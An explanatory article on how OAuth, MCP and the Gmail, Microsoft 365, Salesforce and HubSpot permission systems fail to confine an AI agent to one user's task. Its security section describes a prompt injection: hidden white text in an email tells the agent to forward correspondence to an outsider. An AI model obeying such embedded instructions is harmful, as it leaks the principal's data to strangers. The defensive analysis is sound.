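# Fine-grained permissions for AI agents: limits by sender, recipient, time, task and principal

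## How does an AI agent get access to email and customer records?

An AI agent is software that uses a language model to choose actions and carry them out through tools, such as functions that search a mailbox or update a customer's record. Without tools, a model can only give advice. As *MCP 2026 changes the rules* (Granados, 2026) describes, the model lists the steps and the user carries them out one by one, opening the calendar, sending the email and updating the customer database. An agent that does this work itself needs permission from the systems that hold the mail and the records. It proves it has permission with a credential, usually a token, which is a string of characters it attaches to each request.

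Take Maya, an account manager whose customer Acme is about to renew its contract. She tells her agent: "Until Friday at 17:00, answer Acme's questions about its renewal, using the Acme record in our CRM. Write to nobody new." (A CRM, or customer relationship management system, is the database in which a company keeps its contacts, its deals and its notes on past dealings. Salesforce and HubSpot are two examples.)

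A human assistant would understand from those two sentences that he should read only the mail from Acme, open only one CRM record, reply only to people already in the correspondence, and stop on Friday. Maya is the principal, the person whose authority the agent uses. An operation is an action together with its arguments, such as "send this text to this address", and each of Maya's limits is a constraint on operations. The credential that her agent receives normally includes very few of these constraints because of the way the agent obtains it.

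### From Maya's consent to a token

Most large platforms issue such credentials through OAuth 2.0, an Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) standard defined in *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Hardt, 2012). Before OAuth, people commonly let an outside program use their account by giving it their password. The program could then do whatever the password allowed, and the owner could shut it out only by changing the password, which shut out every other program as well. OAuth instead gives the program its own token, with a stated scope and lifetime.

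The standard has four roles. Maya is the resource owner. The agent's application is the client. The authorisation server issues tokens, and the resource server holds the data and accepts them. Maya's mail and her CRM come from different companies, so she goes through the procedure twice and the agent ends up with separate tokens. For the mail, it runs like this:

1. The agent's developer has already registered the application with the mail provider. The application opens Maya's browser at the authorisation server and passes along its identifier, a return address and the scopes it wants. A scope is a named permission that the platform has fixed in advance, such as "read mail" or "send mail".
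2. The authorisation server signs Maya in and asks whether she grants the request. This is the consent screen. Her password goes to the mail provider and never to the agent.
3. If she agrees, the server sends her browser back to the application with an authorisation code. The code works once, and Hardt recommends that it expire within ten minutes.
4. The application sends the code straight to the authorisation server and receives an access token, often with a refresh token. This direct exchange keeps the tokens out of the browser.
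5. The application attaches the access token to every request. The resource server checks that the token is valid and that its scope covers the request, and then answers.

In Hardt's sample response, the access token lasts one hour. After that, the application presents the refresh token to the authorisation server and gets a new access token with the same or narrower scope. Maya doesn't have to do anything and may not notice. The one-hour expiry therefore doesn't enforce her deadline, because an agent with a working refresh token can still read her mail on Saturday or later, until the refresh token expires or someone revokes it.

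Basic OAuth gives Maya no way to set her limits at the consent screen. The scope field in the request is a list of strings separated by spaces, and the platform decides which strings exist. If it offers "send mail" but not "send mail to Acme until Friday", Maya can either grant the first or give up on the task. Hardt lets the authorisation server grant less than the application asked for, on the owner's instructions, but the smaller grant still comes from the same list. Newer token formats can carry more than a list of names, but the scopes that mail and CRM platforms offer today are mostly coarse.

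### What the server can check

The usual OAuth access token is a bearer token. *The OAuth 2.0 Authorization Framework* (Jones and Hardt, 2012), a companion standard on how to use such tokens, defines a bearer token as one that any holder can use in any way that any other holder can, without proving possession of a cryptographic key. If Maya's token ends up in a log file, whoever reads the log can send mail as Maya until the token expires. Encrypted connections, careful storage and short lifetimes make theft less likely or less harmful, but they don't stop an agent that obtained its token properly from using it for something Maya never asked for.

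When the agent answers a question from Acme, the mail server receives something like this, in simplified form:

```
POST /messages/send
Authorization: Bearer mF_9.B5f...

to:      ortiz@acme.example
subject: Your renewal
text:    The new term would start on 1 March ...
```

The server has the recipient, the text and a token whose scope covers sending mail. Maya's instruction stayed in her conversation with the agent, so the server doesn't have it. The scope check would give the same result if the email were addressed to a competitor.

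*Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) describes this as a gap between operators and operations. An operator is the action alone, such as "transfer money", while an operation includes the amount and the recipient. If a user wants to send $100 to Bob, the bank can check only whether the agent may make transfers. The researchers simulated calls that kept the action but changed the amount or the recipient, and every such call passed a scope check. That is nearly true by definition, since the check doesn't examine the amount or the recipient, so the simulation illustrates the gap more than it measures it. It does show that an attacker can exploit the gap with an ordinary, well-formed request that names a different recipient.

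A resource server can apply rules beyond the scope. The Agentic AI Foundation, an industry body that publishes guidance on agent standards, roughly divides the work between two servers. The authorisation server identifies the caller and determines its permissions, while the resource server checks whether the token is valid there and whether policy allows this particular call. The resource server could therefore check recipients, but someone would have to give it a policy that mentions Acme and Friday, and no step in the flow above does that.

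### The Model Context Protocol

Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), which the AI company Anthropic introduced in 2024. Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* describes it as an open standard that replaces separate custom connections to each data source with a single protocol. A company makes its email or customer records available through an MCP server, which offers a set of tools. The AI application contains an MCP client that calls a tool by name and supplies the arguments. In July 2026, the MCP project counted close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits (Model Context Protocol, 2026). This is evidence of wide use but a poor estimate of the number of agents, because automated builds download the same kits repeatedly.

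MCP standardises tool calls and leaves permission to OAuth. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) makes authorisation optional. An MCP server that supports it over HTTP, the web's ordinary request format, acts as an OAuth resource server, and the client goes through much the same steps as Maya's did. If the agent later tries something its token does not cover, the server should refuse and identify the missing scope, and a client acting for a user should then request a broader token. The new request should combine the scopes the client requested before with the ones it now needs, so that actions that worked earlier do not start to fail. This is sensible, but it means an agent's permissions tend to grow over a long task.

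An MCP server must accept only tokens issued for that server, and it must not pass them on to any other service. A server that connects to an outside mail service therefore needs a separate credential for that service. Maya's agent could hold a narrow token for the MCP server while the MCP server holds a broad one for her mailbox. In that case, only the MCP server's own checks keep the agent within the narrow token's limits.

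The July 2026 version also put the tool's name in a header of each request. A gateway, a service that checks requests between the agent and the platform, can now allow or refuse a call without reading its body. For Maya's agent, the header might contain "send_email". The recipient is still in the body, so a gateway that reads only headers can't restrict who the agent emails, just as a check on scopes can't.

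### Least privilege, the confused deputy and prompt injection

Least privilege is the principle that a program should hold only the permissions its work requires. An agent that files newsletters into a folder doesn't need permission to send mail, and without that permission it cannot send Maya's correspondence to a stranger, even if it goes badly wrong.

MCP tells clients to follow this principle and request only the scopes they need. But if the server has not named the scopes for a request, the client requests every scope on the server's published list. Model Context Protocol (2025), the previous edition of the specification, explains that a general-purpose client usually lacks the knowledge to choose between different services' scopes, so the choice falls to the authorisation server and the user. The list is supposed to contain only the minimum for basic functions, and requesting all of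 it does little damage if the server's operator keeps to that. If the operator lists more, Maya has to decide whether to grant the extra permissions, using a consent screen that names them but does not mention her task.

A confused deputy is a trusted program that someone steers into using its authority for the wrong party. Suppose a firm runs a mail assistant that can open every mailbox, and a trainee asks it for the finance director's messages about redundancies. The trainee has no right to read them. The assistant does, and if it checks only its own permission it will hand them over. Christian Schneider's *Why MCP security is different* finds the same weakness in MCP, which does not inherently carry the user's identity from the application to the server, so that a server with wide privileges may act without any record of who asked. Separate tokens for separate users go a long way towards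 closing that gap, where servers use them. (Readers who consult Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* will find the term attached to a narrower attack, in which a malicious application gains access through consent that the user had earlier given to an intermediary.)

In a prompt injection, an agent reads instructions hidden in content and follows them as if its user had given them. Suppose someone posing as Acme's purchasing department emails Maya a question about the renewal. Below the question, in white type on a white background, the email asks the assistant to forward last month's messages from Acme to an outside address "for audit". The model receives Maya's instruction and the stranger's message in a single stream of text, and it can't reliably tell which one carries her authority. If it complies, the mail server receives a valid token and a request within scope. Protections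 against token theft don't help, because no token was stolen. The agent has become a confused deputy, using Maya's authority for the stranger's purpose.

The rule "write to nobody new" would have stopped that message if something outside the model had enforced it. But it would not have helped if the hidden line had asked the agent to include another customer's discount in its reply to Maya's usual contact at Acme, because that recipient is legitimate. Only a limit on which CRM records the agent may read would help in that case.

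### Standing rules and delegation

Companies already restrict what their software and staff can do with mail. An administrator might set a rule that no mail may leave the company, which the mail system then applies to everyone, at all times and for every task. Maya's instruction to her agent differs because she sets it herself, for one task, and it should expire when that task ends.

Sharma and colleagues call the administrator's rule access control and the user's grant authorisation. In their example, a company caps an agent's spending at $500 per transaction, and a user tells the agent to pay $100. A payment of $499 would be within the company's cap but more than the user authorised.

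Maya's task shows how poorly a standing rule fits a single job. Acme is outside the company, so a ban on outside mail would stop the agent from doing the work. If the administrator relaxes the ban to allow mail to customers, the agent can write to every customer. She could add an exception for Acme and remove it on Friday evening, but doing the same for each task of each employee would amount to writing delegations by hand. The sensible arrangement is to allow an operation only if the company's rules permit it and the user's task calls for it. These two limits differ in who sets them and how long they last, but the same software could in principle check both.

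### Why a broad scope is riskier for an agent

Programs have held broad scopes for years, and most have not misused them. For example, a conventional program that copies customer emails into a CRM needs to read the whole mailbox, because any message could be from a customer. It compares each sender's address with the CRM's list of contacts and saves a copy of the message if it finds a match. Its developer wrote those steps before the program ran. If a customer's email contains a hidden request to forward last month's mail, the program saves the request with the rest of the text. It doesn't forward anything, even if its token allows it to send mail, because its code has no instructions for doing so.

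Such a program always carried some risk. A thief could take its token, an attacker could exploit a flaw to run other code, or a dishonest developer could ship an update that did something new. All of these require the attacker to get hold of the token or change what the program does, but an attacker may be able to misuse an agent's access just by sending it an email.

The consent screen also worked better for conventional software. *Agent Authorization use cases and gap analysis* (Chen, Chen and colleagues, 2026), an IETF working draft with no standing as a standard, observes that OAuth mainly assumes a user who is present and approves a fixed set of permissions at the start. The Agentic AI Foundation likewise notes that traditional OAuth deployments often assume short interactions, whereas an agent's task may run for a long time and need further privileges as new information comes in. In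 the IETF draft's example, a woman asks her assistant on Monday to plan a picnic. On Tuesday afternoon she gets a request for permission to book parks and write to her calendar, with no mention of the picnic. She may not remember why anything would need to book a park, and the request looks much like a phishing attempt. Asking for every permission on Monday would avoid the confusion, but she would be granting them before anyone knows whether the task needs them.

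An agent's developer still sets some limits in code. If he leaves out the tool that deletes messages, the agent cannot call it. But once there is a tool for sending mail, the model chooses the recipient and the text while it runs, after reading messages from people Maya has never met. The program that copied emails used a small, predictable part of what its token allowed, whereas Maya's agent might carry out any operation that its tools and token allow, unless something else checks the arguments.

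## What can Gmail and Microsoft 365 permissions restrict?

Gmail and Microsoft 365 both let Maya give an agent less access than she has, such as permission to read her mail but not send any. But both platforms divide access by action (reading, drafting, sending, deleting) and by mailbox, while most of the limits Maya wants distinguish between messages in the same mailbox. For example, she can't name Acme in a mail permission on either platform.

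### Gmail's 14 scopes

Google documented 14 Gmail scopes as of June 2026, and *Gmail, Calendar, and Drive permissions*, an independent reference, still listed 14 in September. Google sorts them into three tiers. Non-sensitive scopes require only basic app verification, and sensitive scopes require additional verification. Restricted scopes, which give wide access to a user's data, require their own verification, plus a security assessment if the developer stores the data on servers or transmits it.

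| Scope | What the app may do | Tier |
|---|---|---|
| `mail.google.com` | Read, write, send and permanently delete all mail | Restricted |
| `gmail.modify` | Read, write and send, but not permanently delete | Restricted |
| `gmail.readonly` | Read all messages and settings | Restricted |
| `gmail.metadata` | Read labels and headers, but not message bodies | Restricted |
| `gmail.compose` | Manage drafts and send | Restricted |
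| `gmail.send` | Send | Sensitive |
| `gmail.insert` | Add messages to the mailbox | Restricted |
| `gmail.labels` | See and edit labels | Non-sensitive |
| `gmail.settings.basic` | See and change settings and filters | Restricted |
| `gmail.settings.sharing` | Manage sensitive settings, such as who else can manage the mail (administrative use only) | Restricted |
| `gmail.addons.current.message.metadata` | Read the open message's headers | Sensitive |
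| `gmail.addons.current.message.readonly` | Read the open message and the rest of its thread | Sensitive |
| `gmail.addons.current.message.action` | Read the open message when the user interacts with the add-on | Non-sensitive |
| `gmail.addons.current.action.compose` | Manage drafts and send while the user interacts with the add-on | Non-sensitive |

None of these scopes lets Maya limit the agent to a particular correspondent, label, thread or date. `gmail.labels` only lets the agent see and edit the labels themselves, so she can't use it to confine the agent to messages she has labelled "Acme". The add-on scopes come closest, since they apply to whichever message she has open.

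Google's tiers are a poor guide to how much harm an agent could do. Google puts `gmail.send` a tier below `gmail.metadata`, so an app that can send mail as Maya faces a lighter review than one that can only read her headers. That order makes sense if the main worry is a developer who collects people's mail. But Google rates each scope separately, and the danger with an agent often comes from combining two scopes, one that lets it read a stranger's text and another that lets it send Maya's data out.

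The way an agent connects can also require a broad scope. Google advises developers to request `mail.google.com` only if their app must delete mail permanently. However, Google's *Restricted Scopes* also lists any use of IMAP, SMTP and POP3, the older protocols that many ordinary mail programs use, under that scope. An agent that reads Gmail through IMAP would therefore have permission to erase the whole mailbox, even if it never deletes anything.

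### Reading, drafting and sending

The OAuth scope `gmail.readonly` lets an agent read mail but not send it. An agent with only that scope couldn't forward Maya's correspondence through Gmail, though it might still leak the text through another tool, such as a web browser.

Gmail has no scope that lets an agent draft emails but not send them. Many people would like an agent to prepare replies for a person to check, but `gmail.compose` allows both drafting and sending. Even if the agent's developer leaves out the tool for sending, the token still allows it. Maya could instead grant only `gmail.readonly`, read each reply in the agent's own window, and paste the text into Gmail herself.

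Microsoft does separate drafting from sending. Its `Mail.ReadWrite` permission lets an app create, read, update and delete mail, and Microsoft states that it does not include permission to send. An agent with this permission can leave a draft in Maya's mailbox but can't send it. The agent can also delete her mail, because Microsoft offers no permission for drafts alone. A hidden instruction could make the agent erase the Acme thread, but not forward it.

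### Gmail's add-on scopes

A Gmail add-on is a small program that runs in a panel beside the user's mail. Four of Gmail's scopes are only for add-ons and, unlike the other ten, limit access by context.

When Maya opens a message or clicks a button in the add-on, Gmail sends the add-on an event record with the message's identifier and a short-lived access token, which the add-on can use to read that message. According to Google's *Scopes*, the token does not give access to other messages in the mailbox, although `gmail.addons.current.message.readonly` also covers the rest of the open thread. In Google's Gmail scope list, the compose scope includes sending, but the add-on guide mentions only creating drafts and replies, so a cautious administrator should assume that the scope allows sending.

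These scopes would suit the reading half of Maya's task if she opened each of Acme's emails and asked the add-on for a reply, because the add-on would see only that thread. But she wants the agent to answer while she does other work. The token arrives with an event that occurs only when someone opens a message or clicks something, so an unattended agent never receives it. The agent has to use the ordinary scopes, which cover the whole mailbox.

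In May 2025, Google began letting users of add-ons that run on a developer's own servers approve scopes one by one on the consent screen (Google, 2025). Previously, they had to accept or refuse the whole request. Maya could use this to allow reading and refuse sending, but she would still be choosing from the same fixed scopes.

Google Drive's `drive.file` scope covers only files that the app created or that the user opened with it, so the same scope gives access to different files for each user. None of Gmail's 14 scopes works this way. In principle, Gmail could have a similar scope for threads that Maya selects, which an agent could keep using after she closed the window.

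### Delegated and application permissions in Microsoft 365

Programs reach Microsoft 365 data mainly through Microsoft Graph, a single programming interface for mail, calendars, files and other data. Graph has two types of permission. With a delegated permission, an app acts for a signed-in user and can't reach anything the user can't. With an application permission, the app acts under its own identity, with no user signed in, and can reach all the data the permission covers. Only an administrator can grant an application permission.

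Microsoft names permissions on the pattern `{resource}.{operation}.{constraint}`. For example, `Application.ReadWrite.OwnedBy` lets an app manage only the applications that it created or owns. If a name has no constraint, Microsoft says the default is data that the signed-in user owns. But an application permission has no signed-in user. Delegated `Mail.Read` covers Maya's mailbox, while application `Mail.Read` covers every mailbox in her company, so an administrator can't tell from the name alone which one an agent has.

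Microsoft 365 permissions separate operations fairly well. `Mail.ReadBasic` leaves out message bodies and attachments, `Mail.Read` includes them, and `Mail.Send` lets an app send mail without being able to read any. The permissions do much less to limit which mail an app can access. `Mail.Read.Shared` extends access to mail that other people have shared with the user, and even `MailboxFolder.Read` applies to all the user's folders and can't be limited to one.

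Graph does have a constraint called `Selected`, which would suit Maya better. `Lists.SelectedOperations.Selected` limits an app to lists that someone has chosen in SharePoint, Microsoft's system for shared documents and records. Microsoft's permission reference of June 2026 has no `Selected` permission for mail. Google likewise offers a way to choose individual items in Drive but not in email.

Maya may not be able to grant even the delegated permissions herself. Microsoft's reference marks delegated `Mail.Read` as needing no administrator's consent, but an organisation's policy can be stricter. Topedia's *Microsoft-managed default app consent policy now blocks 20 additional permissions* reports that Microsoft extended its recommended policy to more permissions, including some for Outlook mail, and that the change was due to reach customers by late November 2025. In companies that use this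 policy, an administrator has to approve those permissions, but chooses from the same list as Maya would.

### Limiting an app to certain mailboxes

Companies often run an agent under an application permission because the agent serves many employees or works with nobody signed in. By default, this gives the agent access to every mailbox, which is far too much. An administrator can narrow that access with RBAC (role-based access control) for Applications, a feature of Exchange Online, the mail service in Microsoft 365. The administrator writes a filter that selects some mailboxes, registers the app with Exchange, and assigns the app a role, such as "Application Mail.Send", that carries permissions over those mailboxes.

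Office 365 for IT Pros' *Use RBAC for Applications to Control App Use of the Mail.Send Permission* describes a script that emails reports on the health of a company's Microsoft services. With the ordinary application permission, the script could send mail from any mailbox, including the chief executive's. The example restricts the script to one mailbox set aside for sending the reports.

The filter selects the mailboxes that the app may use. It doesn't limit whom the app may write to, although the setting is called `RecipientRestrictionFilter` in the command that creates it. If an administrator sets the filter to Maya's mailbox, the agent can send only as Maya, but it can write to anyone. The administrator can't build a narrower role for "send to Acme" either, because Exchange doesn't allow administrators to copy application roles or derive new ones from them.

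A second mistake is to leave an older, broader grant in place, which can cancel the limit. Administrators usually grant Graph permissions in Entra ID, Microsoft's identity service, and Microsoft's *Role Based Access Control for Applications in Exchange Online* explains that grants made in Exchange add to those made in Entra ID. If the agent already has application `Mail.Read` in Entra ID and the administrator then assigns it `Mail.Read` in Exchange for Maya's mailbox only, the agent can still read every mailbox until the administrator removes the Entra ID grant. Exchange's test command may not reveal the problem, because it ignores permissions from Entra ID. It could report that a colleague's mailbox is out of scope while the agent can still read it.

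Changes can also take between 30 minutes and two hours to apply, because Exchange keeps a temporary copy (a cache) of an app's permissions instead of looking them up for each request. If the administrator removed the agent's role at 17:00 on Friday, a busy agent might keep its access until 19:00. The test command bypasses the cache as well, so it would show the change immediately. Office 365 for IT Pros says that an assignment takes effect immediately, but Microsoft's figure is safer to plan around, particularly when removing access.

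RBAC for Applications doesn't help much if Maya's agent already uses delegated permissions, which limit it to mailboxes she can use. RBAC for Applications reduces a company-wide agent's access to roughly that level.

### Can mail flow rules limit whom an agent writes to?

Exchange does have a way to restrict addressees. Its mail flow rules inspect messages in transit and can reject, redirect or copy them. Each rule has conditions, exceptions and actions. An administrator could reject everything from a given sender unless the recipient belongs to Acme:

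```
New-TransportRule "Write only to Acme"
  -From maya@ourfirm.example
  -ExceptIfRecipientDomainIs acme.example
  -RejectMessageReasonText "Not an Acme address"
```

This rule would also stop Maya from writing to anyone else. Microsoft's *New-TransportRule* lists dozens of conditions, including ones for senders, recipients, subject lines and attachments, but none for the application that submitted the message. The rule therefore applies equally to messages the agent sends as Maya and messages she sends herself.

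Two of the available conditions could help identify an agent's messages, but neither does so reliably. A rule can look for a particular header, which the agent's software could add to every message it sends. But a misbehaving agent, or a thief with its token, could leave out the header and escape the rule. A rule can also check the IP address from which a message arrived. According to Microsoft, that is the address of the last machine before the message reached its service, which may not be the original sender's.

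Giving the agent a separate mailbox works better. RBAC for Applications can restrict the agent to sending from an address such as `renewals@ourfirm.example`, and a mail flow rule can restrict where mail from that address goes without affecting Maya's own mail. Together, the two features limit which recipients this one app can email, as long as nothing else uses the mailbox and no leftover grant lets the agent send from another.

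The administrator has to choose the exception carefully, because some Exchange recipient conditions act on each recipient separately, while others act on the whole message if any recipient matches. If he writes an exception of the second kind for Acme addresses, and the agent sends one email to Acme's buyer and a stranger, the buyer's address triggers the exception and the stranger gets the email too. With the exception in the example above, Exchange should reject the stranger's copy and deliver the buyer's.

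"Write to nobody new" is harder to express because no condition refers to past correspondence. A rule for Acme's domain allows mail to Acme's subdomains and to every Acme employee, including people Maya has never written to. The administrator could instead list the permitted addresses one by one. One condition matches recipients on the sender's own list of allowed addresses, but it's a remnant of Live@edu, an older Microsoft service for schools, and Microsoft 365 customers can't add entries to the lists.

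Mail flow rules can start at a set time. An administrator could create one that rejects every message from the agent's mailbox and set it to start on Friday at 17:00. The agent could still read mail after that, because mail flow rules act only on messages in transit.

If Exchange can't finish processing a mail flow rule, it ignores the rule by default, according to Microsoft's *Explore mail flow rules*. That is reasonable for a rule that adds a disclaimer to outgoing mail, but a rule meant to contain an agent should not let the message through when processing fails. For such a rule, the administrator should set Exchange to resubmit the message instead.

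### Have the companies added permissions for agents?

Microsoft has created a separate kind of identity for AI agents, called Entra Agent ID, which lets administrators see and control their agents in one place. Microsoft says agent identities use the same Graph permissions as other apps, except for some of the most powerful ones, which it blocks. For example, even an administrator cannot give an agent permission to manage every user account.

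This removes permissions that could damage a whole organisation but does not change access within one mailbox. Microsoft says an agent may still have delegated `Mail.Read`, for example, because it reaches only one user's data. Microsoft's longer list of blocked permissions includes several for files, chats and calendars but none for mail. Agent identities can also inherit permissions from a shared template, so an administrator approves them once for all the agents made from it. This avoids a lot of repeated approvals, but it encourages permissions that suit a type of agent more than any one task.

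According to Microsoft's documentation, agents can hold only less privileged administrative roles, but the list of permitted roles includes Exchange Administrator. A person needs this Entra ID role to assign permissions through RBAC for Applications. A company that relies on mailbox limits to contain an agent should not give it this role, because the agent might then be able to change its own limits.

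*Mail-Advanced.ReadWrite*, an entry in an online catalogue of Graph permissions, describes a newer permission that also divides access by action. It covers changing the contents of messages that are no longer drafts, again without sending. It requires an administrator's consent, and the catalogue lists no Graph operations that use it yet. Microsoft's own reference didn't include it in June 2026. Even if it becomes widely used, it won't help Maya separate Acme's messages from anyone else's.

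Google's June list of Gmail scopes had none specifically for agents, and the count of 14 in September suggests that Google hadn't added one by then.

### The closest fit for Maya's task

In Gmail, the narrowest grant that lets the agent work unattended is `gmail.readonly` plus `gmail.send`. This avoids the power to delete or alter mail that comes with `gmail.modify`. Compared with what Maya asked for, the agent can also:

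- read every message in her mailbox, from any sender and any year, along with her settings
- send any text to any address
- carry on after Friday at 17:00, for as long as it can renew its token.

The Microsoft 365 equivalents are delegated `Mail.Read` and `Mail.Send`. They grant almost the same excess access, except that `Mail.Read` doesn't include mailbox settings. To get a refresh token, an app also requests the `offline_access` permission. Microsoft's standard sign-in library requests it by default, so a developer may include it without considering how long the agent needs access.

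An administrator could get closer in Microsoft 365 by combining the features above. The agent would have its own mailbox, and RBAC for Applications would restrict it to that mailbox. One mail flow rule would copy Acme's messages to Maya into the agent's mailbox, a second would reject the agent's replies to anyone except the Acme contacts Maya already knows, and a third would block everything the agent sends from 17:00 on Friday. The agent would have no access to Maya's mailbox. Maya would have to forward the earlier correspondence herself, because the first rule copies only new mail. Acme would also receive answers from an unfamiliar address.

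The agent would still have more access than it needs. It would receive Acme's emails on every subject, including, say, an invoice dispute unrelated to the renewal. It could send the permitted contacts anything it had read. It could also keep reading its mailbox after the deadline, until the administrator removed its role and the cache updated. Maya couldn't set up any of these restrictions without the administrator, and he would have to repeat most of the work for her next customer.

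## What can Salesforce and HubSpot permissions restrict?

Salesforce's scopes can't specify individual records, so to confine an agent to the Acme record, an administrator must narrow the user account the agent works under or build a special tool for it. HubSpot's scopes are finer and separate reading contacts from editing deals, for example, but they can't specify individual records either. In both systems, Maya can do little on her own except accept or refuse the permissions the agent's developer requests.

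### What Salesforce's scopes open

Salesforce sorts its data into objects, which are types of record. An account is a company, a contact is a person, and an opportunity is a possible sale. Maya's "Acme record" is one account plus the contacts and the renewal opportunity attached to it. Each record has fields, such as a phone number or a discount.

The OAuth scopes mostly determine which of Salesforce's programming interfaces an app may use on the user's behalf. Salesforce's *Scope Parameter Values* lists more than 20, of which three matter most here:

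- `api` lets an agent work with the user's data through the main interfaces, including one for handling records in bulk.
- `full` gives access to all the data the user can reach, and includes every other scope.
- `refresh_token`, also called `offline_access`, lets the agent obtain a refresh token.

The `full` scope doesn't return a refresh token unless the app also requests `refresh_token`. An agent with `full` alone would therefore lose access when its session ended, while an agent with `api` and `refresh_token` could keep copying customer records for months.

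The list has no read-only version of `api`. Even if Maya's agent only looks up renewal dates, its token would also let it change them if Maya can. An app can also get more access than it needs if its developer leaves the scopes out. In Salesforce's software kit for mobile apps, such an app receives every scope configured for it.

### Objects, fields and records

Salesforce then applies the user's own permissions, which are much more detailed. Every user has a profile that sets baseline permissions, and an administrator can add more through permission sets. Together, these determine which objects the user can create, read, update or delete, and which fields the user can see or edit.

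The company controls access to individual records separately, starting with a default for each object. If accounts are private by default, for example, an ordinary user sees the accounts she owns and any shared with her. Sharing rules give particular people or groups access to more records.

Suppose Maya can read and edit accounts but not delete them, can't see the field that holds her company's costs, and has access to 60 customers. An agent that signs in as Maya has the same access. If it follows a hidden instruction to delete Acme's account or report the company's costs, Salesforce blocks it. If the instruction is to copy another customer's discount into an email to Acme, Salesforce provides the discount because Maya is allowed to see it.

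So these permissions stop the agent from exceeding Maya's job, but her job covers 60 customers and this task covers one.

### A separate user for the agent

The administrator could instead create a Salesforce user just for the agent. He would let it read accounts, contacts and opportunities, hide the fields it doesn't need, and share only Acme's records with it. Salesforce would then refuse the agent's request for any other customer's discount, whatever the model had read in an email. This comes closest to Maya's "using the Acme record".

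Using sharing rules to limit an agent works only if the company keeps the relevant objects private by default. These rules can only add access, so if every employee can already read every account, the agent's user can too. Changing the default would affect everyone else in the company.

The arrangement also isn't tied to the task. When Maya starts her next renewal, the administrator must share that customer's records and remember to stop sharing Acme's. If he keeps forgetting, the agent's user will gradually gain access to the records of all 60 of Maya's customers.

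Salesforce (2026) calls it an anti-pattern for all agents to connect through MCP as one shared user. That setup would turn every employee's agent into a confused deputy, and the logs would show the same name for every action. Giving Maya's agent its own user with narrow permissions avoids most of the confused deputy problem. The logs would still show the agent's user instead of Maya, so the company would need another record of who gave the instruction.

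### What Salesforce's hosted MCP servers add

An agent can reach a company's Salesforce data through MCP servers that Salesforce runs. The only way to connect is for a person to sign in through a browser using OAuth, and every tool call runs with that person's permissions. Salesforce says the servers don't support service accounts or machine-to-machine connections. A dedicated user account for the agent would therefore work only if someone could sign in as that user, which seems contrary to the design's intent.

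Salesforce says this arrangement keeps a human in the loop, but the human only connects the agent and grants it access. The recommended setup includes `refresh_token`, so the agent can later read or change a record without Maya present.

During the beta, an app needed four scopes, including the broad `api`. According to Salesforce's *Transition from Beta*, these are replaced by `refresh_token` and `mcp_api`, which covers only the hosted MCP servers. An agent with these two scopes can use the servers' tools but not Salesforce's ordinary interfaces. This reduces the agent's access, but how much depends on which tools the company turns on.

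All the servers are off until an administrator enables them. Salesforce's *Best Practices* describes four ready-made servers for working with records:

| Server | What an agent can do |
|---|---|
| `sobject-reads` | Read records |
| `sobject-mutations` | Create and update records, but not delete them |
| `sobject-deletes` | Delete records |
| `sobject-all` | All of the above |

`sobject-reads` suits Maya's agent, which only has to answer questions. However, an administrator can't restrict a particular app to a particular server. If the administrator enables `sobject-all` because a colleague's agent needs it, the `mcp_api` scope on Maya's agent covers that server too. Her agent may never connect to it, because someone still has to enter the server's address in the agent's settings, but her token wouldn't prevent the connection, and only her own permissions would.

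The administrator can get closer to the task with a Named Query, a database query that he writes in advance and offers to the agent as a tool. For Maya, it might look like this:

```
SELECT Name, Renewal_Date__c, Renewal_Price__c
FROM Account
WHERE Name = 'Acme'
```

The agent can run this query but can't change it, so the tool returns only three fields about one customer. This doesn't require a separate user. But if `sobject-reads` is also on, the agent could use that server to look up every other customer. To prevent this, the administrator would have to leave the general servers off for the whole company or rely on the agent's settings to stop it from using them.

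For more complicated conditions, a developer can write a custom tool in Apex, Salesforce's programming language. Such a tool could, for example, reject requests after Friday at 17:00. The company using Salesforce has to write, test and maintain the rule itself.

Tools can also have annotations that describe them as read-only or destructive. Many agents use these to decide when to ask for confirmation. Salesforce warns that they are hints and that some clients ignore them, so annotations don't limit what an agent can do.

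### Who can connect to Salesforce, and for how long?

An agent connects to a hosted server through an external client app, an entry the administrator creates to register the agent's software with Salesforce. By default, any user in the company can sign in through it. According to Salesforce's *Create an External Client App*, the administrator can restrict it to people with a certain permission set or to connections from certain IP addresses. The address restriction isn't always practical, because some AI services connect from more addresses than Salesforce's list can hold.

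The same guide states that refresh tokens stay valid indefinitely by default. In June 2026, Salesforce's developer blog gave the default as one year, and the *Salesforce MCP Server Setup Guide*, a sample from Amazon's cloud business, AWS, tells administrators to set 365 days. Administrators should check the actual setting rather than assume either default. Salesforce advises 30 days or less, along with rotation, which replaces the refresh token each time the agent uses it and cancels the old one.

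A thirty-day limit would leave Maya's agent with access for more than three weeks after her deadline, though it is reasonable protection against a thief who finds an old token. The administrator could choose a shorter period, but the setting applies to the whole app, so every colleague who uses the same agent would also have to sign in more often.

Salesforce has a similar-sounding but weaker rule for its partners. Its *Secure Your Connected Apps and External Client Apps* required partners whose apps serve more than two customers to make refresh tokens expire after 30 days without use, by 11 May 2026. Each use restarts the 30 days, so the token of an agent that checks for mail every hour would never expire under this rule. The partners must also rotate tokens and accept refresh requests only from listed IP addresses. These measures protect only against token theft, such as the theft of Salesloft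 Drift tokens in 2025.

The administrator can end the agent's access on Friday at 17:00 by manually revoking its token. He can also turn on single logout, so that revoking Maya's Salesforce session also ends the agent's. Salesforce logs calls to its hosted MCP servers under Maya's name but marks them as MCP traffic, which should help him tell the agent's actions from hers.

### HubSpot's scopes

HubSpot builds more of its limits into the scopes. An agent needs `crm.objects.companies.read` to read companies and `crm.objects.deals.write` to edit deals. Contacts, tickets, invoices and other types of data have their own scopes. In HubSpot's more expensive plans, fields that a company has marked as sensitive or highly sensitive require further scopes, so a token that can read ordinary contact details can't necessarily read fields such as health information.

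HubSpot describes the `crm.objects.companies.write` scope as permission to view companies as well as create, change and delete them. With this scope, Maya can't let an agent correct Acme's address without also letting it delete Acme's record.

Since 8 September 2026, developers have been able to replace HubSpot's remaining broad scopes with narrower ones, such as separate scopes for reading and writing. But according to HubSpot's *Update your app to granular scopes*, the recommended update selects the new scopes that preserve the app's current access. If the developer does nothing, HubSpot eventually applies an update to keep the app working. An old app therefore keeps the same access, with a longer list of permissions, unless its developer chooses the customised update and removes some.

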